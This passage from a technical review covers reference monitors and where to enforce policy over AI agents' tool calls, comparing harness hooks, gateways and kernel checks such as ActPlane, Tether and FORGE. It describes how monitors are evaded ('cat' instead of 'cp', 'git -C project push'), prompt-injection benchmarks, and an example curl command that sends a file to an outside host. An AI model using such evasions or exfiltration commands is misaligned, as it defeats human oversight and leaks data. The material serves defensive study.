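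This tolerance may not extend to policies that depend on history, where one missed event can make later decisions wrong. This risk may have made companies reluctant to adopt general monitors, but the adoption record contains no direct evidence that it did.

### The work of writing policies

There is stronger evidence that writing policies discourages users. The SecurityManager's users did not have to rewrite programs, yet its developers blame low adoption partly on the difficulty of working out which permissions a program needs. OpenSearch reports the same complaint from plug-in authors, who often did not learn that an operation needed permission until it failed.

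Even experts make mistakes with these policies. Search Guard's *LDAP Authentication Broken in Elasticsearch 8.18.0* describes how Elasticsearch's own developers omitted `outbound_network` from one module's policy. The module could no longer connect to the servers that held users' accounts, and users noticed the mistake because legitimate logins through those servers failed. Search Guard sells a competing security plug-in and has an interest in publicising such errors, but the article identifies a specific one.

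Outside developers have trouble too. In *I have a custom search plugin that I can install*, eereiter describes trying to grant a plug-in permission to create a class loader and then trying to turn the checks off. The reply was that outside plug-ins can't have that permission and nobody can disable the checks.

CFI avoids most of this work, because the compiler derives the permitted destinations from the program. A developer only has to enable an option, but CFI may crash programs that call functions through pointers of the wrong type or mix C with assembly code, unless the developer adds exceptions. Houy, Kreyssig and colleagues (2025), in *SoK*, say that developers get no guidance on applying CFI to real software. If even this much work slows the adoption of a fixed policy, a system that also requires a list of methods and a set of rules will probably spread more slowly.

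### Who can rewrite a program

A monitor also needs someone who wants the checks and has the authority to insert them. Microsoft has that motive and authority for Windows because it builds the system and has to deal with attacks on it. On Linux, as Houy and Bartel point out, enabling CFI is mostly up to each application's developers, and hardly any have done so. This comparison supports the explanation, but technical obstacles may also explain the difference. Google had to patch the original CFI implementation before it worked on Android, and Linux distributions lack an equivalent set of general fixes.

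Native Client met the same condition in a different way. Chrome refused to run programs without the required checks, so developers who wanted their programs to run in Chrome had to add them. OpenSearch and Elasticsearch load plug-ins into a process they control, and they have reason to distrust code from other developers. By contrast, someone who used Aurasium or AppGuard had to modify an app without its developer's cooperation.

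Broken signatures were an obstacle on Android, but they can't explain why few inlined monitors reached production elsewhere. A company that rewrites its own program can sign the result, and a Java agent changes classes only after they have been read from the package, so the package's signature stays valid.

Support contracts could discourage rewriting in a similar way. In the forum thread *ES 8.19.5 encountered a NotEntitledException when attach to the ES process*, a user wanted to attach a diagnostic agent to Elasticsearch and learned that Elastic doesn't support this. Elastic's documentation also warns that third-party agents can harm stability. So a company may insert checks into its own product while discouraging customers from adding their own. One company's position doesn't show that support terms held back the research systems.

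### When platforms add or remove the function

Platforms have often built in the simplest uses of inlining, as Android 6 did with its new permissions and browsers did with Content Security Policy. Users got these features through ordinary updates, which no research prototype could offer. But the features came too late to explain why SASI and Naccio had so few users.

Java is the opposite case. OpenSearch used Java's built-in SecurityManager while it was available. After OpenJDK decided to remove it, OpenSearch's developers built an inlined monitor, because operating-system controls couldn't distinguish between plug-ins. This is good evidence that a built-in mechanism can suppress demand for inlining, though it comes from a program whose developers already had policies they wanted to keep.

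The best-supported explanations are that policies took too much work and that few people had both a reason to rewrite a program and the authority to do it. Platform features and run-time overhead explain some cases. How support contracts and gaps in coverage affected adoption remains conjecture.

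## Where to check an agent's tool calls: inside the harness, at a gateway or in the operating system

OpenSearch could check its plug-ins because it controls the process that runs them. Developers of AI agents likewise control the harness, so they can put a check at its dispatch hook, the point just before it executes a tool call. They can also check calls in a gateway, a separate process that forwards calls to the tools, or in the operating system, when a tool acts on files, programs or network connections.

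### What carries over from inlined monitors

A dispatch hook works like an inserted check because it runs immediately before the action and can refuse it. A rewriter reads the target's code and adds a check at each relevant call, but a language model has no such code to rewrite or certify beforehand. The harness instead sends tool calls through one dispatcher. A hook there resembles a callee-side check, which runs no matter how the program reached the method.

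The untrusted code is also in a different place. SASI and PoET had to protect their variables from the program that contained them. A harness is usually trusted code, written by a developer who wants the checks to work, and the model can only send it requests. But the programs that tools start may not be trustworthy, and the model may have written some of them. A dispatch hook can't check what these programs do, just as a bytecode rewriter couldn't check native code. Earlier systems also moved checks to a lower level. ConScript moved its checks into the script engine, and the Android Security Framework moved AppGuard's decisions into the operating system.

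### One tool call at three placements

Suppose an agent calls a tool named `read_file` to read `/data/r.txt`. Toyoda, Leung and U (2026), in *guardscope*, use this call to show what a check can read at each placement. In simplified form:

```
Harness hook:      read_file(path="/data/r.txt"), plus the session's context
Gateway:           {"name": "read_file", "arguments": {"path": "/data/r.txt"}}, plus headers
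Operating system:  openat "/data/r.txt", by process p, which process q started
```

The hook has the most information about the purpose of the call, because it can read the rest of the session. It runs in the harness's process, so the harness has to keep the model and any programs that tools start from accessing the hook's code and policy. The hook can check only the calls that the harness dispatches.

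The gateway reads the same tool name and arguments, but it has little information about the session unless the harness supplies it. It can also examine the tool's response. Microsoft's *Securing MCP* describes a toolkit that scans each tool's description for hidden instructions and inspects each response before the model receives it. A process boundary protects the gateway from the agent, and the gateway can hold the keys to outside services so that the agent never has them.

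A gateway checks only the calls routed through it, so a careful deployment ensures that calls bypassing it fail. *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026) describes a gateway for cloud systems that accept only the gateway's own credential. Mr. Hide protected Android permissions in much the same way, by taking them away from the app.

*ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) puts the check in the Linux kernel using eBPF, which runs small programs there. At this level, a `read_file` tool call appears only as a process opening a file. A privileged process loads the rules before the agent starts, and the agent can later add rules for itself but can't weaken the existing ones. The kernel part has about 1,800 lines of code. Zheng and colleagues leave the policy compiler out of the trusted computing base, which seems too generous because the compiler also translates the rules that the agent can't change.

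ActPlane can check an operation by any process that descends from the agent, provided it has a hook for that operation. It can therefore enforce a version of the file-and-message policy across several programs. A process that reads a secret file receives a label, which spreads to the files it writes and the processes it starts. A rule then blocks network connections from any process with that label. Labels accumulate, so in a long session the rule may begin to block harmless connections.

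Each placement leaves some actions unchecked, because a check can evaluate only the actions that reach it.

### Measured delays

Microsoft (2026) reports a delay for the policy engine in its Agent Governance Toolkit, and Zheng and colleagues timed individual system calls. Ameur, Bouzefrane and Banerjee (2026) built a proxy that runs beside the agent's client, and *SchemaCaps*, their paper, gives the best figure for proxies.

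| Check | Placement | Added delay |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft's policy engine | Harness or gateway | Under 0.1 ms for 99% of actions |
| SchemaCaps | Proxy | 0.47 ms per call, 1.1 ms per request for the list of tools |
| ActPlane with 32 rules | Kernel | About 0.006 ms per file opened, 0.067 ms per program started |

These figures can't rank the placements, because they measure different things. Microsoft's figure appears to cover only evaluating the rules. SchemaCaps' figure includes checking the arguments and applying a policy, and it ranged from 0.37 to 0.56 ms over five runs of 500 calls. A single tool call can also cause many kernel events. ActPlane would add about 63 ms to a call that opened 10,000 files.

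In longer tests with 32 rules, ActPlane slowed a replay of an agent's tool actions by 1.9% and a build of the Linux kernel by 6.5%. No rule fired in any of these tests, so the results exclude the time needed to handle a violation. Zheng and colleagues say a single turn of a language model takes 2 to 10 seconds, so none of these delays would be noticeable. Although SASI's x86 prototype was very slow, run-time overhead gives little reason to prefer one placement over another for agents.

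Rare decisions can take much longer. SchemaCaps exists because tool servers change the arguments their tools accept. Version 0.1.35 of Desktop Commander, for example, let the agent choose which shell would run a command, so a policy written for one shell's commands no longer determined what could run. When such a change arrives, the proxy holds calls while it decides whether the change gives the agent more authority. The median decision took 22 ms, but the slowest took 10.5 seconds.

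### What guardscope measured

To measure which actions a control evaluates in practice, Toyoda and colleagues listed 15 paths by which a model's decision can take effect and eight arrangements of checks, from none to a check in the kernel. For each pair, they worked out whether the arrangement would check an action on that path, miss it, or prevent it by other means, such as a network filter. The table gives the main arrangements and leaves out paths whose outcome depends on the deployment.

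| Arrangement | Paths checked, out of 15 | Control in the test |
|---|---|---|
| Gateway for tool servers reached over HTTP | 1 | Microsoft's toolkit, agentgateway |
| Gateway for all tool servers, with direct network traffic blocked | 3 | Microsoft's toolkit |
| The harness's own permission checks | 5 | Pi |
| Permission checks plus a gateway | 5 | Pi and Microsoft's toolkit |
| Policy engine inside the harness | 5 | Pi |
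| Kernel | 13 | ActPlane |

They then ran 15 fixed actions under each arrangement. The main tests used the Pi harness; a second harness, OpenClaw, gave identical counts with the basic gateway. The test program replayed the actions without calling a model, so that every run was the same. Before each run, the control had to refuse one forbidden action to prove it was working. A separate sensor in the kernel recorded what happened, and guardscope compared this record with the control's own log.

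The harness's permission checks and a gateway together evaluated all seven calls to tool servers but none of the other eight actions. ActPlane evaluated seven of those eight actions but none of the calls to tool servers, so combining it with the other controls would have covered 14 of the 15 actions. Adding the gateway to the permission checks made more detail available for the policy but did not increase the number of actions evaluated.

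Toyoda and colleagues conclude that where a control is placed determines both what it covers and what detail is available to it. The kernel can observe the most paths, but it works with file names and process numbers, while the harness works with tools and sessions.

The measurements only partly support this conclusion, because the workload exercised four of the 15 paths and the other counts come from analysis. The kernel's count of 13 is an upper limit. The analysis counts calls to tool servers as covered by a kernel check, but ActPlane's hooks evaluated none of them. ActPlane also loaded on only one of the three kernel versions the researchers tried, which suggests that a kernel check takes more work to deploy. The researchers compiled the list of paths from real harnesses, in discussion with two AI models, so it may be incomplete. Also, guardscope measures whether a control evaluated an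 action, not whether its decision was right.

### The case for a separate process

NVIDIA's OpenShell runtime enforces policy outside the agent's process, which NVIDIA compares to the way a browser isolates its tabs. NVIDIA argues that even a compromised agent can't override such a policy, whereas the protections in tools like Claude Code and Cursor "live inside the agent". It adds that model output can't influence enforcement outside the process. This is a strong argument against relying on prompts, but a weaker one against a dispatch hook, which is also ordinary code outside the model, unless the agent can alter the harness.

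Millstone, Akidau and colleagues (2026), in *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary*, make a more detailed case. An agent that works with a person's credentials can reach everything the person can, but lacks the person's judgment about what belongs to the job. If somebody asks it to summarise the issues in one engineering project, its credentials may let it read many other projects too. Their proxy, Out-of-Band Policy Enforcement (OBPE), handles a call in these steps:

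1. It identifies the agent from information that the platform attaches, which the agent can't change.
2. A connector translates the call into a typed action on a particular resource.
3. The policy allows the call, refuses it or holds it for somebody's decision.
4. The proxy narrows an allowed request, for example by adding a filter to a query.
5. When the service replies, the proxy removes or masks protected records and fields before the model receives them.

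The data owner writes a policy that sets the most any agent may do, and each agent's own policy can only narrow it. Where rules overlap, OBPE takes the most restrictive result, much as conjunction does in Polymer. Millstone and colleagues prove that the order of the rules doesn't matter and that an agent's policy can't exceed the owner's. The proof assumes that every relevant call and response passes through the proxy and that the connector describes them completely.

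The connector thus has the same role as Naccio's platform interface, and somebody has to maintain it. Maintaining it is harder for responses than for requests. Millstone and colleagues cite a 2026 count in which only 234 of the 1,856 tools on 100 popular servers declared their output format.

They tested a simplified version on 71 tasks with simulated Jira and ServiceNow systems and four models. A run failed if protected data reached the model, if the answer contained an exact protected value, or if a forbidden change took effect. With six data-handling rules in the prompt, 57.6% of runs failed. After they added OBPE, 0.2% failed. Giving each family of similar tasks equal weight, they estimate that OBPE reduced the failure rate by 41.2 percentage points. Agents also completed fewer tasks with OBPE, 60.9% instead of 79.1%, partly because the policy was supposed to refuse or hold 12 of the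 71.

In a separate comparison on one model, 58.6% of runs still failed when a second language model reviewed the agent's answers. By the time of the review, the data had already reached the model and any change had taken effect.

The experiment is good evidence for checking calls and responses in ordinary code instead of relying on instructions or later review. It doesn't show that the code has to run in a separate process, because Millstone and colleagues didn't compare OBPE with a hook in the harness that applied the same rules.

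### The case for a hook in the harness

Microsoft argues that governance belongs at the action layer, and fits its toolkit into the middleware pipeline of its agent framework. In the guardscope tests, the toolkit's policy module ran as a gateway, so choosing a set of rules doesn't determine where they must be checked.

*Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) makes this point explicitly. Its check, ScopeGate, can run inside the application, in a proxy on the same machine or at a central gateway. In one test, a simulated payment agent tried to change a merchant's payout account to an attacker's. The framework's normal dispatcher made the change, while ScopeGate refused because the account was not on a verified list. The paper claims that security doesn't depend on the placement, as long as every call with side effects goes through the check and the agent can't reach the policy. These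 conditions are hard to meet, and guardscope's results suggest that placement largely determines whether a deployment meets them.

A hook is also easier to install. *Stop Means Stop* (2026) describes a monitor called SoundGate and, in a demonstration, adds it at the single point through which a framework's tool calls pass, without modifying the framework. An optional checker searches the source code for calls that bypass this point, but it misses those made through dynamic dispatch, which was also a problem for caller-side rewriters. For stronger protection, a deployment can isolate the tools' network so that they can reach only the machine with the gate, or intercept their actions in the kernel, but both take more work to integrate.

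The best evidence for giving a check access to the agent's context comes from Zheng and colleagues, who advocate kernel enforcement. They collected 1,361 policies from the instruction files that 64 software projects give their agents. They judged that operating-system hooks could enforce 607 of them, such as a ban on deleting certain data. Most of the others depend on the contents of a file or on how the agent reasons and writes. A harness hook can at least read the text that an agent asks to write to a file.

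### What each layer adds

Several designs check tool calls in more than one place. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) nests three boundaries. The outermost checks whether the tool call is permitted, the next restricts the process that runs the tool, and the innermost confines that process's files, memory and network connections.

*AgentKernel* (2026) describes a design that also passes information from one layer to the next. Simple rules check the call at the tool boundary in under a millisecond. Before the tool runs, a privileged program works out which files and network addresses the tool may use and installs that list in the kernel. If the tool or any process it starts goes outside the list, the program pauses that process. The kernel thus enforces a policy made for a single call, although the list still has to be correct.

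In *AgentBouncer* (2026), a language model judges whether a system call is necessary and safe, given the task and the tool call behind it. The system holds the call until the model answers, and stores the answer for repeated requests. This gives a low-level check some information about the agent's purpose. But Anderson required that a reference monitor be open to complete analysis, and nobody can analyse a language model completely.

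*Kairos* (2026) argues that a monitor at the system boundary often can't determine whether the user authorised an effect. A plain yes-or-no check would therefore refuse legitimate work or let attacks through. Like an edit automaton, Kairos can hold an effect back while the agent continues, and it has a similar limit. It can keep changes to stored data in a staging area and discard them later, but if the agent needs a reply from somebody outside, it has to wait.

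Layers also need to pass information back to the agent. Zheng and colleagues tested ActPlane on 190 recorded coding tasks, 114 of which broke a rule. ActPlane detected 77.2% of the violations, while three checks at the tool-call level each detected 34% to 40%. The agent corrected itself after 97.7% of detections when ActPlane told it which rule it had broken and how to comply, but after 31.4% when it received only a generic refusal.

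The test favoured checking in the kernel, because two-thirds of the violations were designed to produce the forbidden effect indirectly, and a check on tool calls has the least information about indirect effects. ActPlane also intervened wrongly in 18 of the 76 cases that obeyed the rules, mostly because a translated rule was too broad.

Adding a layer doesn't always make the combined policy stricter. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) describes a harness with a guard that checks web requests and a sandbox that has no network access. If the guard approves a request, the harness sends it from outside the sandbox, so the sandbox's network restriction doesn't apply. Two layers enforce both policies only if every action must pass both.

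### Accounting for coverage

A monitor's own log can't show what the monitor missed. *Agent-Safety Evaluations as Load-Bearing Evidence* (2026) proposes a coverage ratio, the share of an agent's risky steps that a monitor scored. In its example, a payments monitor scored one of three risky steps, for a ratio of 0.333. The monitor scored neither of the two steps that changed data, so the ratio fell to zero when the team counted only those steps as risky. The ratio depends on how the team defines "risky". It also doesn't show what information the monitor had or whether its judgments were right.

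Such a ratio covers only the steps that appear in the record. This is why guardscope uses a separate kernel sensor, and why *Agent-Warden* (2026) treats kernel observation as a complement to application traces. The kernel's record doesn't identify the tool call behind an operation, so somebody has to match the two records afterwards.

A gateway can record some of the missing information when it handles a call. *Observability for Delegated Execution in Agentic AI Systems* (Mishra and Sharad, 2026) gives an example in which one agent works on two assignments at once, reading and writing in Google Drive, Slack and Confluence. The ordinary logs aren't enough to determine which actions belong to which assignment, so Mishra and Sharad's gateway attaches the assignment's identity to each tool call. They add that a log must distinguish an action that had no assignment from one whose assignment wasn't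 recorded, or an investigator can't tell unauthorised work from a gap in the monitoring.

*Mandato* (Racioppi, 2026) proposes a proxy that checks each call against a digitally signed authorisation and links its log entries cryptographically, so that later changes can be detected. Tool servers would accept connections only from the proxy, which would make the log complete for those servers. Mandato is still being built. Racioppi plans to test it by restarting the proxy and interrupting its decision service, then comparing the log with the calls that reached the servers. Any call missing from the log would count as a defect.

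## Writing policies over agent tool calls

A monitor can read a tool call's name and arguments, but someone has to write the rules it applies. Designers of earlier monitors learned that policies need meaningful events, a record of those events, and a way to resolve conflicts. Several agent systems from 2026 test how well these lessons apply to tool calls.

### One policy over typed tools and over a shell

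*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) presents one Dogwood policy for two kinds of tool. Dogwood is a language from Amazon Web Services (AWS) whose rules can refer to earlier tool calls. The policy protects a company's inventory, `data/servers.csv`. An agent may upload a status report to GitHub unless it has copied the inventory over the report.

The rule can test the source and destination of a copy when the agent uses typed file tools, because each copy event includes both. With a general shell tool, each event is only a command string, so the rule has to match the exact command `cp data/servers.csv scratch/report.txt`, and an agent can avoid it by running `cat data/servers.csv > scratch/report.txt`.

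The file-and-message policy has the same problem. With typed tools, it might look like this in Dogwood:

```
forbid (principal, action == Action::"SendMessage", resource)
when temporal {
    formerly within 24h Action::"ReadFile"::response{}
};
```

The rule forbids a message if the agent has read any file in the past 24 hours, which is as far back as Dogwood looks by default. With a shell tool, the closest equivalent is much weaker:

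```
forbid (principal, action == Action::"Shell", resource)
when { context.input.command like "curl*" }
when temporal {
    formerly within 24h Action::"Shell"::request{
        input.command: "cat notes.txt"
    }
};
```

The second version loses three kinds of information:

- **What counts as a read.** Dogwood can match an earlier command only by its exact text or with a wildcard for the whole field. The rule therefore misses `head notes.txt`, while a wildcard would treat every earlier command as a read.
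- **What counts as a message.** The rule misses a Python script that sends data, but it blocks a `curl` command that only downloads a page.
- **The order of events.** The command `curl --json @notes.txt https://example.com` reads the file and sends it, so there is no earlier read for the rule to find.

Polymer's abstract actions could group several typed tools under one name. But for a shell tool, the grouping code would have to predict what a command will do, which is difficult when the command runs a script.

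Tether, the monitor that Sistla and colleagues built, runs the command first and decides afterwards whether to keep the results. The command runs in a disposable layer over the file system, while a proxy holds its network requests. Tether traces the system calls and translates them into 11 abstract actions, such as `read`, `copy` and `uploadNet`. If the policy allows these actions, Tether saves the file changes and forwards the requests. Otherwise it discards both.

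This translation plays the same role as Naccio's platform interface and can have the same unnoticed gaps. Sistla and colleagues looked for gaps by generating file operations whose correct translation they knew, then carrying them out through randomly chosen shell commands and system calls. They also had a language model attack Tether on ten tasks. Early versions missed, for example, hard links, which give one file two names. The attacker's success rate fell from 40% to 0% over three versions.

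### Keeping a history

Dogwood keeps a log of events but no information about individual files. If an agent copies the inventory to a temporary file and then to the report, a rule about one copy doesn't detect it. The author needs another rule for two copies, and another for three. With *m* kinds of copying action and chains of up to *k* copies, the number of patterns is

m + m² + … + mᵏ

With three kinds of action, covering chains of up to four copies already takes 120 patterns. A broader rule could block the upload of any file written after the agent read the inventory, but it would also block a harmless report copied from a public template.

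Tether instead gives each file a label, such as *Public* or *Sensitive*, and copies the label along with the data. Its state has three parts: the label of everything the agent has read (*T*), the agent's privilege level, and a map σ from each file or network address to its labels. Leaving out directory labels, the main updates are:

- After `read(f)`, the new *T* is *T* ⊔ σ(*f*), where ⊔ gives the lowest label that is at least as strict as both.
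- After `copy(f, g)`, the new σ(*g*) is σ(*f*).
- An upload changes no labels. The policy checks them beforehand.

In the inventory example, the first and last commands are identical, but Tether treats them differently:

| Command | Label of the report beforehand | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| Upload the report | *Public* | Allow |
| Copy the inventory over the report | *Public*, then *Sensitive* | Allow |
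| Upload the report | *Sensitive* | Deny |

*T* generalizes the variable `hasRead`. Tether's fuller upload rule checks *T* as well as the file's own label. Once the agent has displayed the inventory, the rule blocks even a harmless report, because the agent might have included what it read.

Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, derive the history when they need it. Their monitor, FORGE, records messages, tool calls and results in a graph, with an edge wherever one event may have influenced another. Policies use Datalog, a logic language for querying databases. The file-and-message policy needs three rules, in which `:-` means "if":

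```
HasRead(e) :- FileRead(e).
HasRead(e) :- DependsOn(e, d), HasRead(d).
Deny(a)    :- Send(a), HasRead(a).
```

The second rule applies repeatedly, so it follows a chain of any length. When an agent attempts an action, FORGE proceeds as follows:

1. It finds the message that led to the action and waits until the policy engine has received all the events behind that message.
2. It collects facts about the action, the user's verified identity and the recorded events.
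3. The Datalog engine derives everything that the rules imply.
4. FORGE blocks the action if the engine derived `Deny`. If the engine derived only `Allow`, the action runs. If it derived neither, a default applies.

A model's output depends on every message in its history, so for a single agent these rules act much like `hasRead`. With several agents, the rules are more precise, because one agent's read affects another agent's message only if a recorded chain of events connects them.

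Approvals work the same way. Palumbo and colleagues applied FORGE to MALADE, a group of agents that looks for links between drugs and health problems. An agent may query the US Food and Drug Administration's drug labels only if its user has the right role and a supervisor's approval appears earlier in the same session. In 15 trials without FORGE, the agents made 40 unauthorised queries. With FORGE they made none, and they still reached the correct answer in all 15 trials.

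### What Tether and FORGE guarantee

Sistla and colleagues wrote Tether's policy language in Lean, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. They proved that the order of rules doesn't matter, that adding a permissive rule can't cancel a denial, and that a denied action leaves the state unchanged. In Polymer, programmers had to ensure the last property themselves by keeping updates out of `query`.

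They also proved seven properties of one particular policy, for every starting state and every finite sequence of actions. One is that an agent that starts without secret data never receives data labelled *Secret*. A language model helped to write the proofs, but Lean checks them, so nobody has to trust the model. The proofs start from the abstract actions, so they assume that Tether has correctly translated the system calls into those actions.

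FORGE guarantees that an action never runs if the policy derives a denial for it, provided that every relevant action reaches the monitor and the recorded facts are accurate. A program that opens a raw network socket, for example, bypasses FORGE.

Palumbo and colleagues treat extra edges in the graph as safe because they can only cause more blocking, which is true for the three rules above but not for every policy. For example, an extra edge could connect a query to an approval meant for something else, and FORGE would then allow the query.

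### When a classifier has to guess

Some policies depend on conditions that no exact test can decide. In one demonstration of FORGE, a personal assistant may tell a manager when somebody is busy but not why. The policy uses a language model to check whether each reply reveals a reason. This check caught a reply that mentioned doctor's appointments, and the assistant's second attempt gave only times. If the model had missed the appointments, FORGE would have applied the rules correctly and still released private information.

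*Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (Solko-Breslin, Mudrakarta and colleagues, 2026) keeps the classifier's probabilities instead of turning them into yes or no. Suppose an agent wants to send text that depends on two messages, and a classifier gives one a 45% chance of containing confidential information and the other a 25% chance. A monitor that counts only scores above 50% treats both as harmless, but the chance that at least one is confidential could be as high as 70%.

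The exact chance depends on how the two events are related, which the monitor usually doesn't know. In another example, an agent redacts file A, merges the result with file B and sends the merged file. File A has a 90% chance of being sensitive, the redaction tool has a 10% chance of failing, and file B has a 20% chance of being sensitive. The risk that the merged file is sensitive is:

- If the events are independent: 0.9 × 0.1 = 0.09 for file A, and 0.09 + 0.2 − 0.09 × 0.2 = 27.2% overall.
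- In the worst case: min(0.9, 0.1) = 0.1 for file A, and 0.1 + 0.2 = 30% overall.

A monitor that blocks at 30% would allow the transfer under the first calculation and stop it under the second. Assuming independence can cause much larger errors than this. If a tool that fails 10% of the time redacts the same file twice, independence gives a 1% chance that both attempts fail. But if the first attempt misses some text, the second will probably miss it too.

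An exact worst-case calculation has to consider 2ⁿ combinations for *n* facts, which takes too long during a run. Solko-Breslin and colleagues use a faster approximation that never underestimates the risk but may overestimate it and block a safe action.

The guarantee is therefore weaker than FORGE's, because the monitor only keeps the probability of a violation below a chosen limit instead of ensuring that forbidden actions never run. Even this weaker guarantee requires that the classifier's error rates are accurate and that attackers can't change them. Solko-Breslin and colleagues assume this, but the assumption is strong when an attacker may have written the text that the classifier reads.

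### Allow, ask and deny

FORGE and Tether both let a denial override any permission. This shortens Polymer's ranking of suggestions to two levels, with deny above allow. Rules that only allow or deny can't propose incompatible replacements, the way Polymer's policies can. But FORGE can also alter a web request, for instance by adding a password, and the ranking doesn't determine how to combine two such changes.

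Tether can combine whole policies in two ways. With `require`, both policies must allow an action, so if each policy permits only its own separate activity, the combination permits neither, as with Polymer's conjunction. With `grant`, either policy can allow an action, but the added policy applies only when no rule in the main policy covers the action, and every required policy must still allow it. A policy author can therefore use `grant` to add permissions without weakening an existing prohibition.

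Many actions are neither clearly safe nor clearly forbidden, so some systems can also ask a person. The proxy that Millstone and colleagues built can hold a call until somebody decides. When several rules apply, it follows the most restrictive one, so deny overrides ask, and ask overrides allow. Sistla and colleagues suggest that Tether could also ask a person about some of the calls it denies.

Ranking "ask" in this way leaves a problem when two policies return it for different reasons. Suppose one returns "ask" because the recipient is new, and the other because the file is confidential. If the person sees only the question about the recipient, their approval shouldn't settle the question about the file. Polymer avoids this by querying both policies again after the answer, although the person may then have to answer twice.

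*Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) runs a series of checks, called gates, until one refuses the call. The order of the gates doesn't change whether a call is refused, but it can change the reason the agent receives, which comes only from the first gate to refuse. The agent may use that reason to plan its next step. If a gate crashes, the call goes ahead. This prevents a bug in a gate from blocking legitimate calls, but it also means that a bug can disable a check.

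### When checks improve task success

Reddy and colleagues tested their gates on τ²-bench, a benchmark in which agents serve simulated customers. Its airline tools carry out any well-formed request, even one that breaks the airline's written policy. For example, an agent can cancel a ticket the customer has no right to cancel, and the tool reports no error. With gpt-4o-mini, a small model from 2024, 78% of failed runs ended with the database in an incorrect state and no error from any tool.

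Four gates checked each change against the database before it took effect. Palumbo and colleagues tested FORGE on the same benchmark with Claude Opus 4.5, GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview. The table gives the share of runs that completed the task.

| Tasks and checks | Agent | Without checks | With checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Airline, four gates | gpt-4o-mini | 29.6% | 42.0% |
| The same, with new random seeds | gpt-4o-mini | 30.8% | 43.1% |
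| Airline, four gates | gpt-5.2 | 61.2% | 71.6% |
| Airline, FORGE | Average of three models | 74.7% | 81.5% |
| Retail, FORGE | Average of three models | 86.3% | 87.4% |

The checks helped because they turned a hidden mistake into a refusal that the agent could respond to. On the 26 tasks where a gate refused something, gpt-4o-mini's success rate rose by 19.2 percentage points. The 5.0-point rise on the other 24 tasks could be chance. Nearly all of FORGE's airline gain also came from task-model combinations where it blocked at least one action.

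The gain is smaller in retail, plausibly because the retail tools already refuse many forbidden requests. When Reddy and colleagues tried gates on eight retail tasks, success fell from 62.5% to 57.8%, though the drop could also be chance.

Reddy and colleagues repeated the gpt-4o-mini test with 15 new runs per task, but did not repeat the gpt-5.2 test. They tested the gates on the same tasks they wrote them for, and didn't test whether stating the gates' rules more forcefully in the prompt would work just as well. In one task, though, a customer lies about the facts, so a clearer rule would not have helped. Gated agents solved that task in all 16 runs, and ungated agents in at most one of 16.

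### What stricter policies cost

Checks reduced task success on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which tool results contain malicious instructions. Palumbo and colleagues ran it five times with GPT-4o, with 97 ordinary tasks and 949 attacks per run. In every row below, the agent received the user's request again after each batch of tool results.

| Added defence | Successful attacks | Ordinary tasks completed |
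|---|---|---|
| None | 14.1% | 83.7% |
| A model chooses which tools the agent may use | 3.1% | 73.4% |
| FORGE, checking where each argument came from | 0.9% | 62.5% |
| FORGE, blocking important actions after untrusted input | 0.6% | 33.2% |

The last two rows use the same monitor, so the difference between them comes from the policies. The stricter policy blocks important actions once the agent has read untrusted text, even if the user asked for them. The other policy can still allow actions the user requested, and under it nearly twice as many tasks succeeded with almost the same security. Some attacks on the final answer still worked because an agent can give a false answer without making a tool call for the monitor to check.

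With 32 agents running at once, FORGE's median decision time was 0.19 milliseconds at the monitor and 0.72 milliseconds as measured by the agent's program. Agents lost more time recovering from refusals, because they had to request approval and try again. This raised the average time of a MALADE trial from 59.4 to 67.3 seconds.

Sistla and colleagues tested Tether by replaying recorded sessions of coding agents. Tether stopped all 344 attacks and interrupted 74 of 1,590 harmless sessions, or 4.7%. Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a language model reviews each command, stopped 91.6% of the attacks and interrupted 9.7% of the harmless sessions. When the researchers gave Auto Mode their policy as text, the figures were 89.2% and 3.5%.

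The comparison includes only sessions whose actions Tether can model, which favours Tether. It excludes, for example, database queries, background processes, and attacks that consist of harmful code in a file the agent may edit. Replayed sessions also can't show whether an agent would have recovered from a refusal. Tether's tracing tool slowed the experiments considerably, and Sistla and colleagues propose replacing it.

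### Who writes the policies, and their mistakes

Researchers wrote or supervised all of these policies, so there is little evidence about how well ordinary developers would write them. The policies are also fairly long. FORGE's airline policy has several dozen rules, which Palumbo and colleagues translated from the benchmark's written instructions. Tether's has 24 rules, plus labels and lists of permitted files and hosts that somebody has to adjust for each task.

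Reddy and colleagues provide the best evidence on errors, because they compared each refusal with the benchmark's correct solution:

| Gate | Refusals | Correct refusals |
|---|---|---|
| Is the booking eligible for cancellation? | 161 | 100% |
| Has the agent read the record it wants to change? | 90 | 78% |
| Does the baggage change follow the rules? | 42 | 5% |
| Does the change alter the number of passengers? | 9 | 100% |

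The baggage gate was wrong 40 times out of 42. The cancellation gate produced most of the improvement in task success, and it was the only gate whose removal made the agent less successful. Even a correct refusal could interfere with a task if the agent kept making the forbidden request.

Some of FORGE's policy rules are easy to satisfy by accident or to avoid. The airline policy requires the customer to confirm a booking, but it accepts a confirmation from anywhere in the conversation, so confirming one booking also satisfies the rule for the next. Another policy requires a coding agent to run security scans before it publishes code, and detects publication by the text `git push` in a shell command. If that is the whole test, `git -C project push` avoids it. An injected instruction could tell the agent to write the command differently, although Palumbo and colleagues argue that prompt injection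 can't bypass this policy.

Language models can help draft policies. FORGE includes a translator that turns written instructions into Datalog. Palumbo and colleagues warn that it may omit or invent conditions, so they check that every instruction has a rule and that every rule is based on the instructions. Sistla and colleagues had a model propose Tether's policy, tested the draft on benchmark sessions, checked it against the seven properties in Lean, and repeated the process until the policy worked well. The Lean check rejects drafts that break a stated property, but it doesn't cover properties that nobody thought to state. Because the researchers refined the policy on sessions from the same benchmarks they used to measure its 4.7% rate of wrong interruptions, the rate may be higher on new work.
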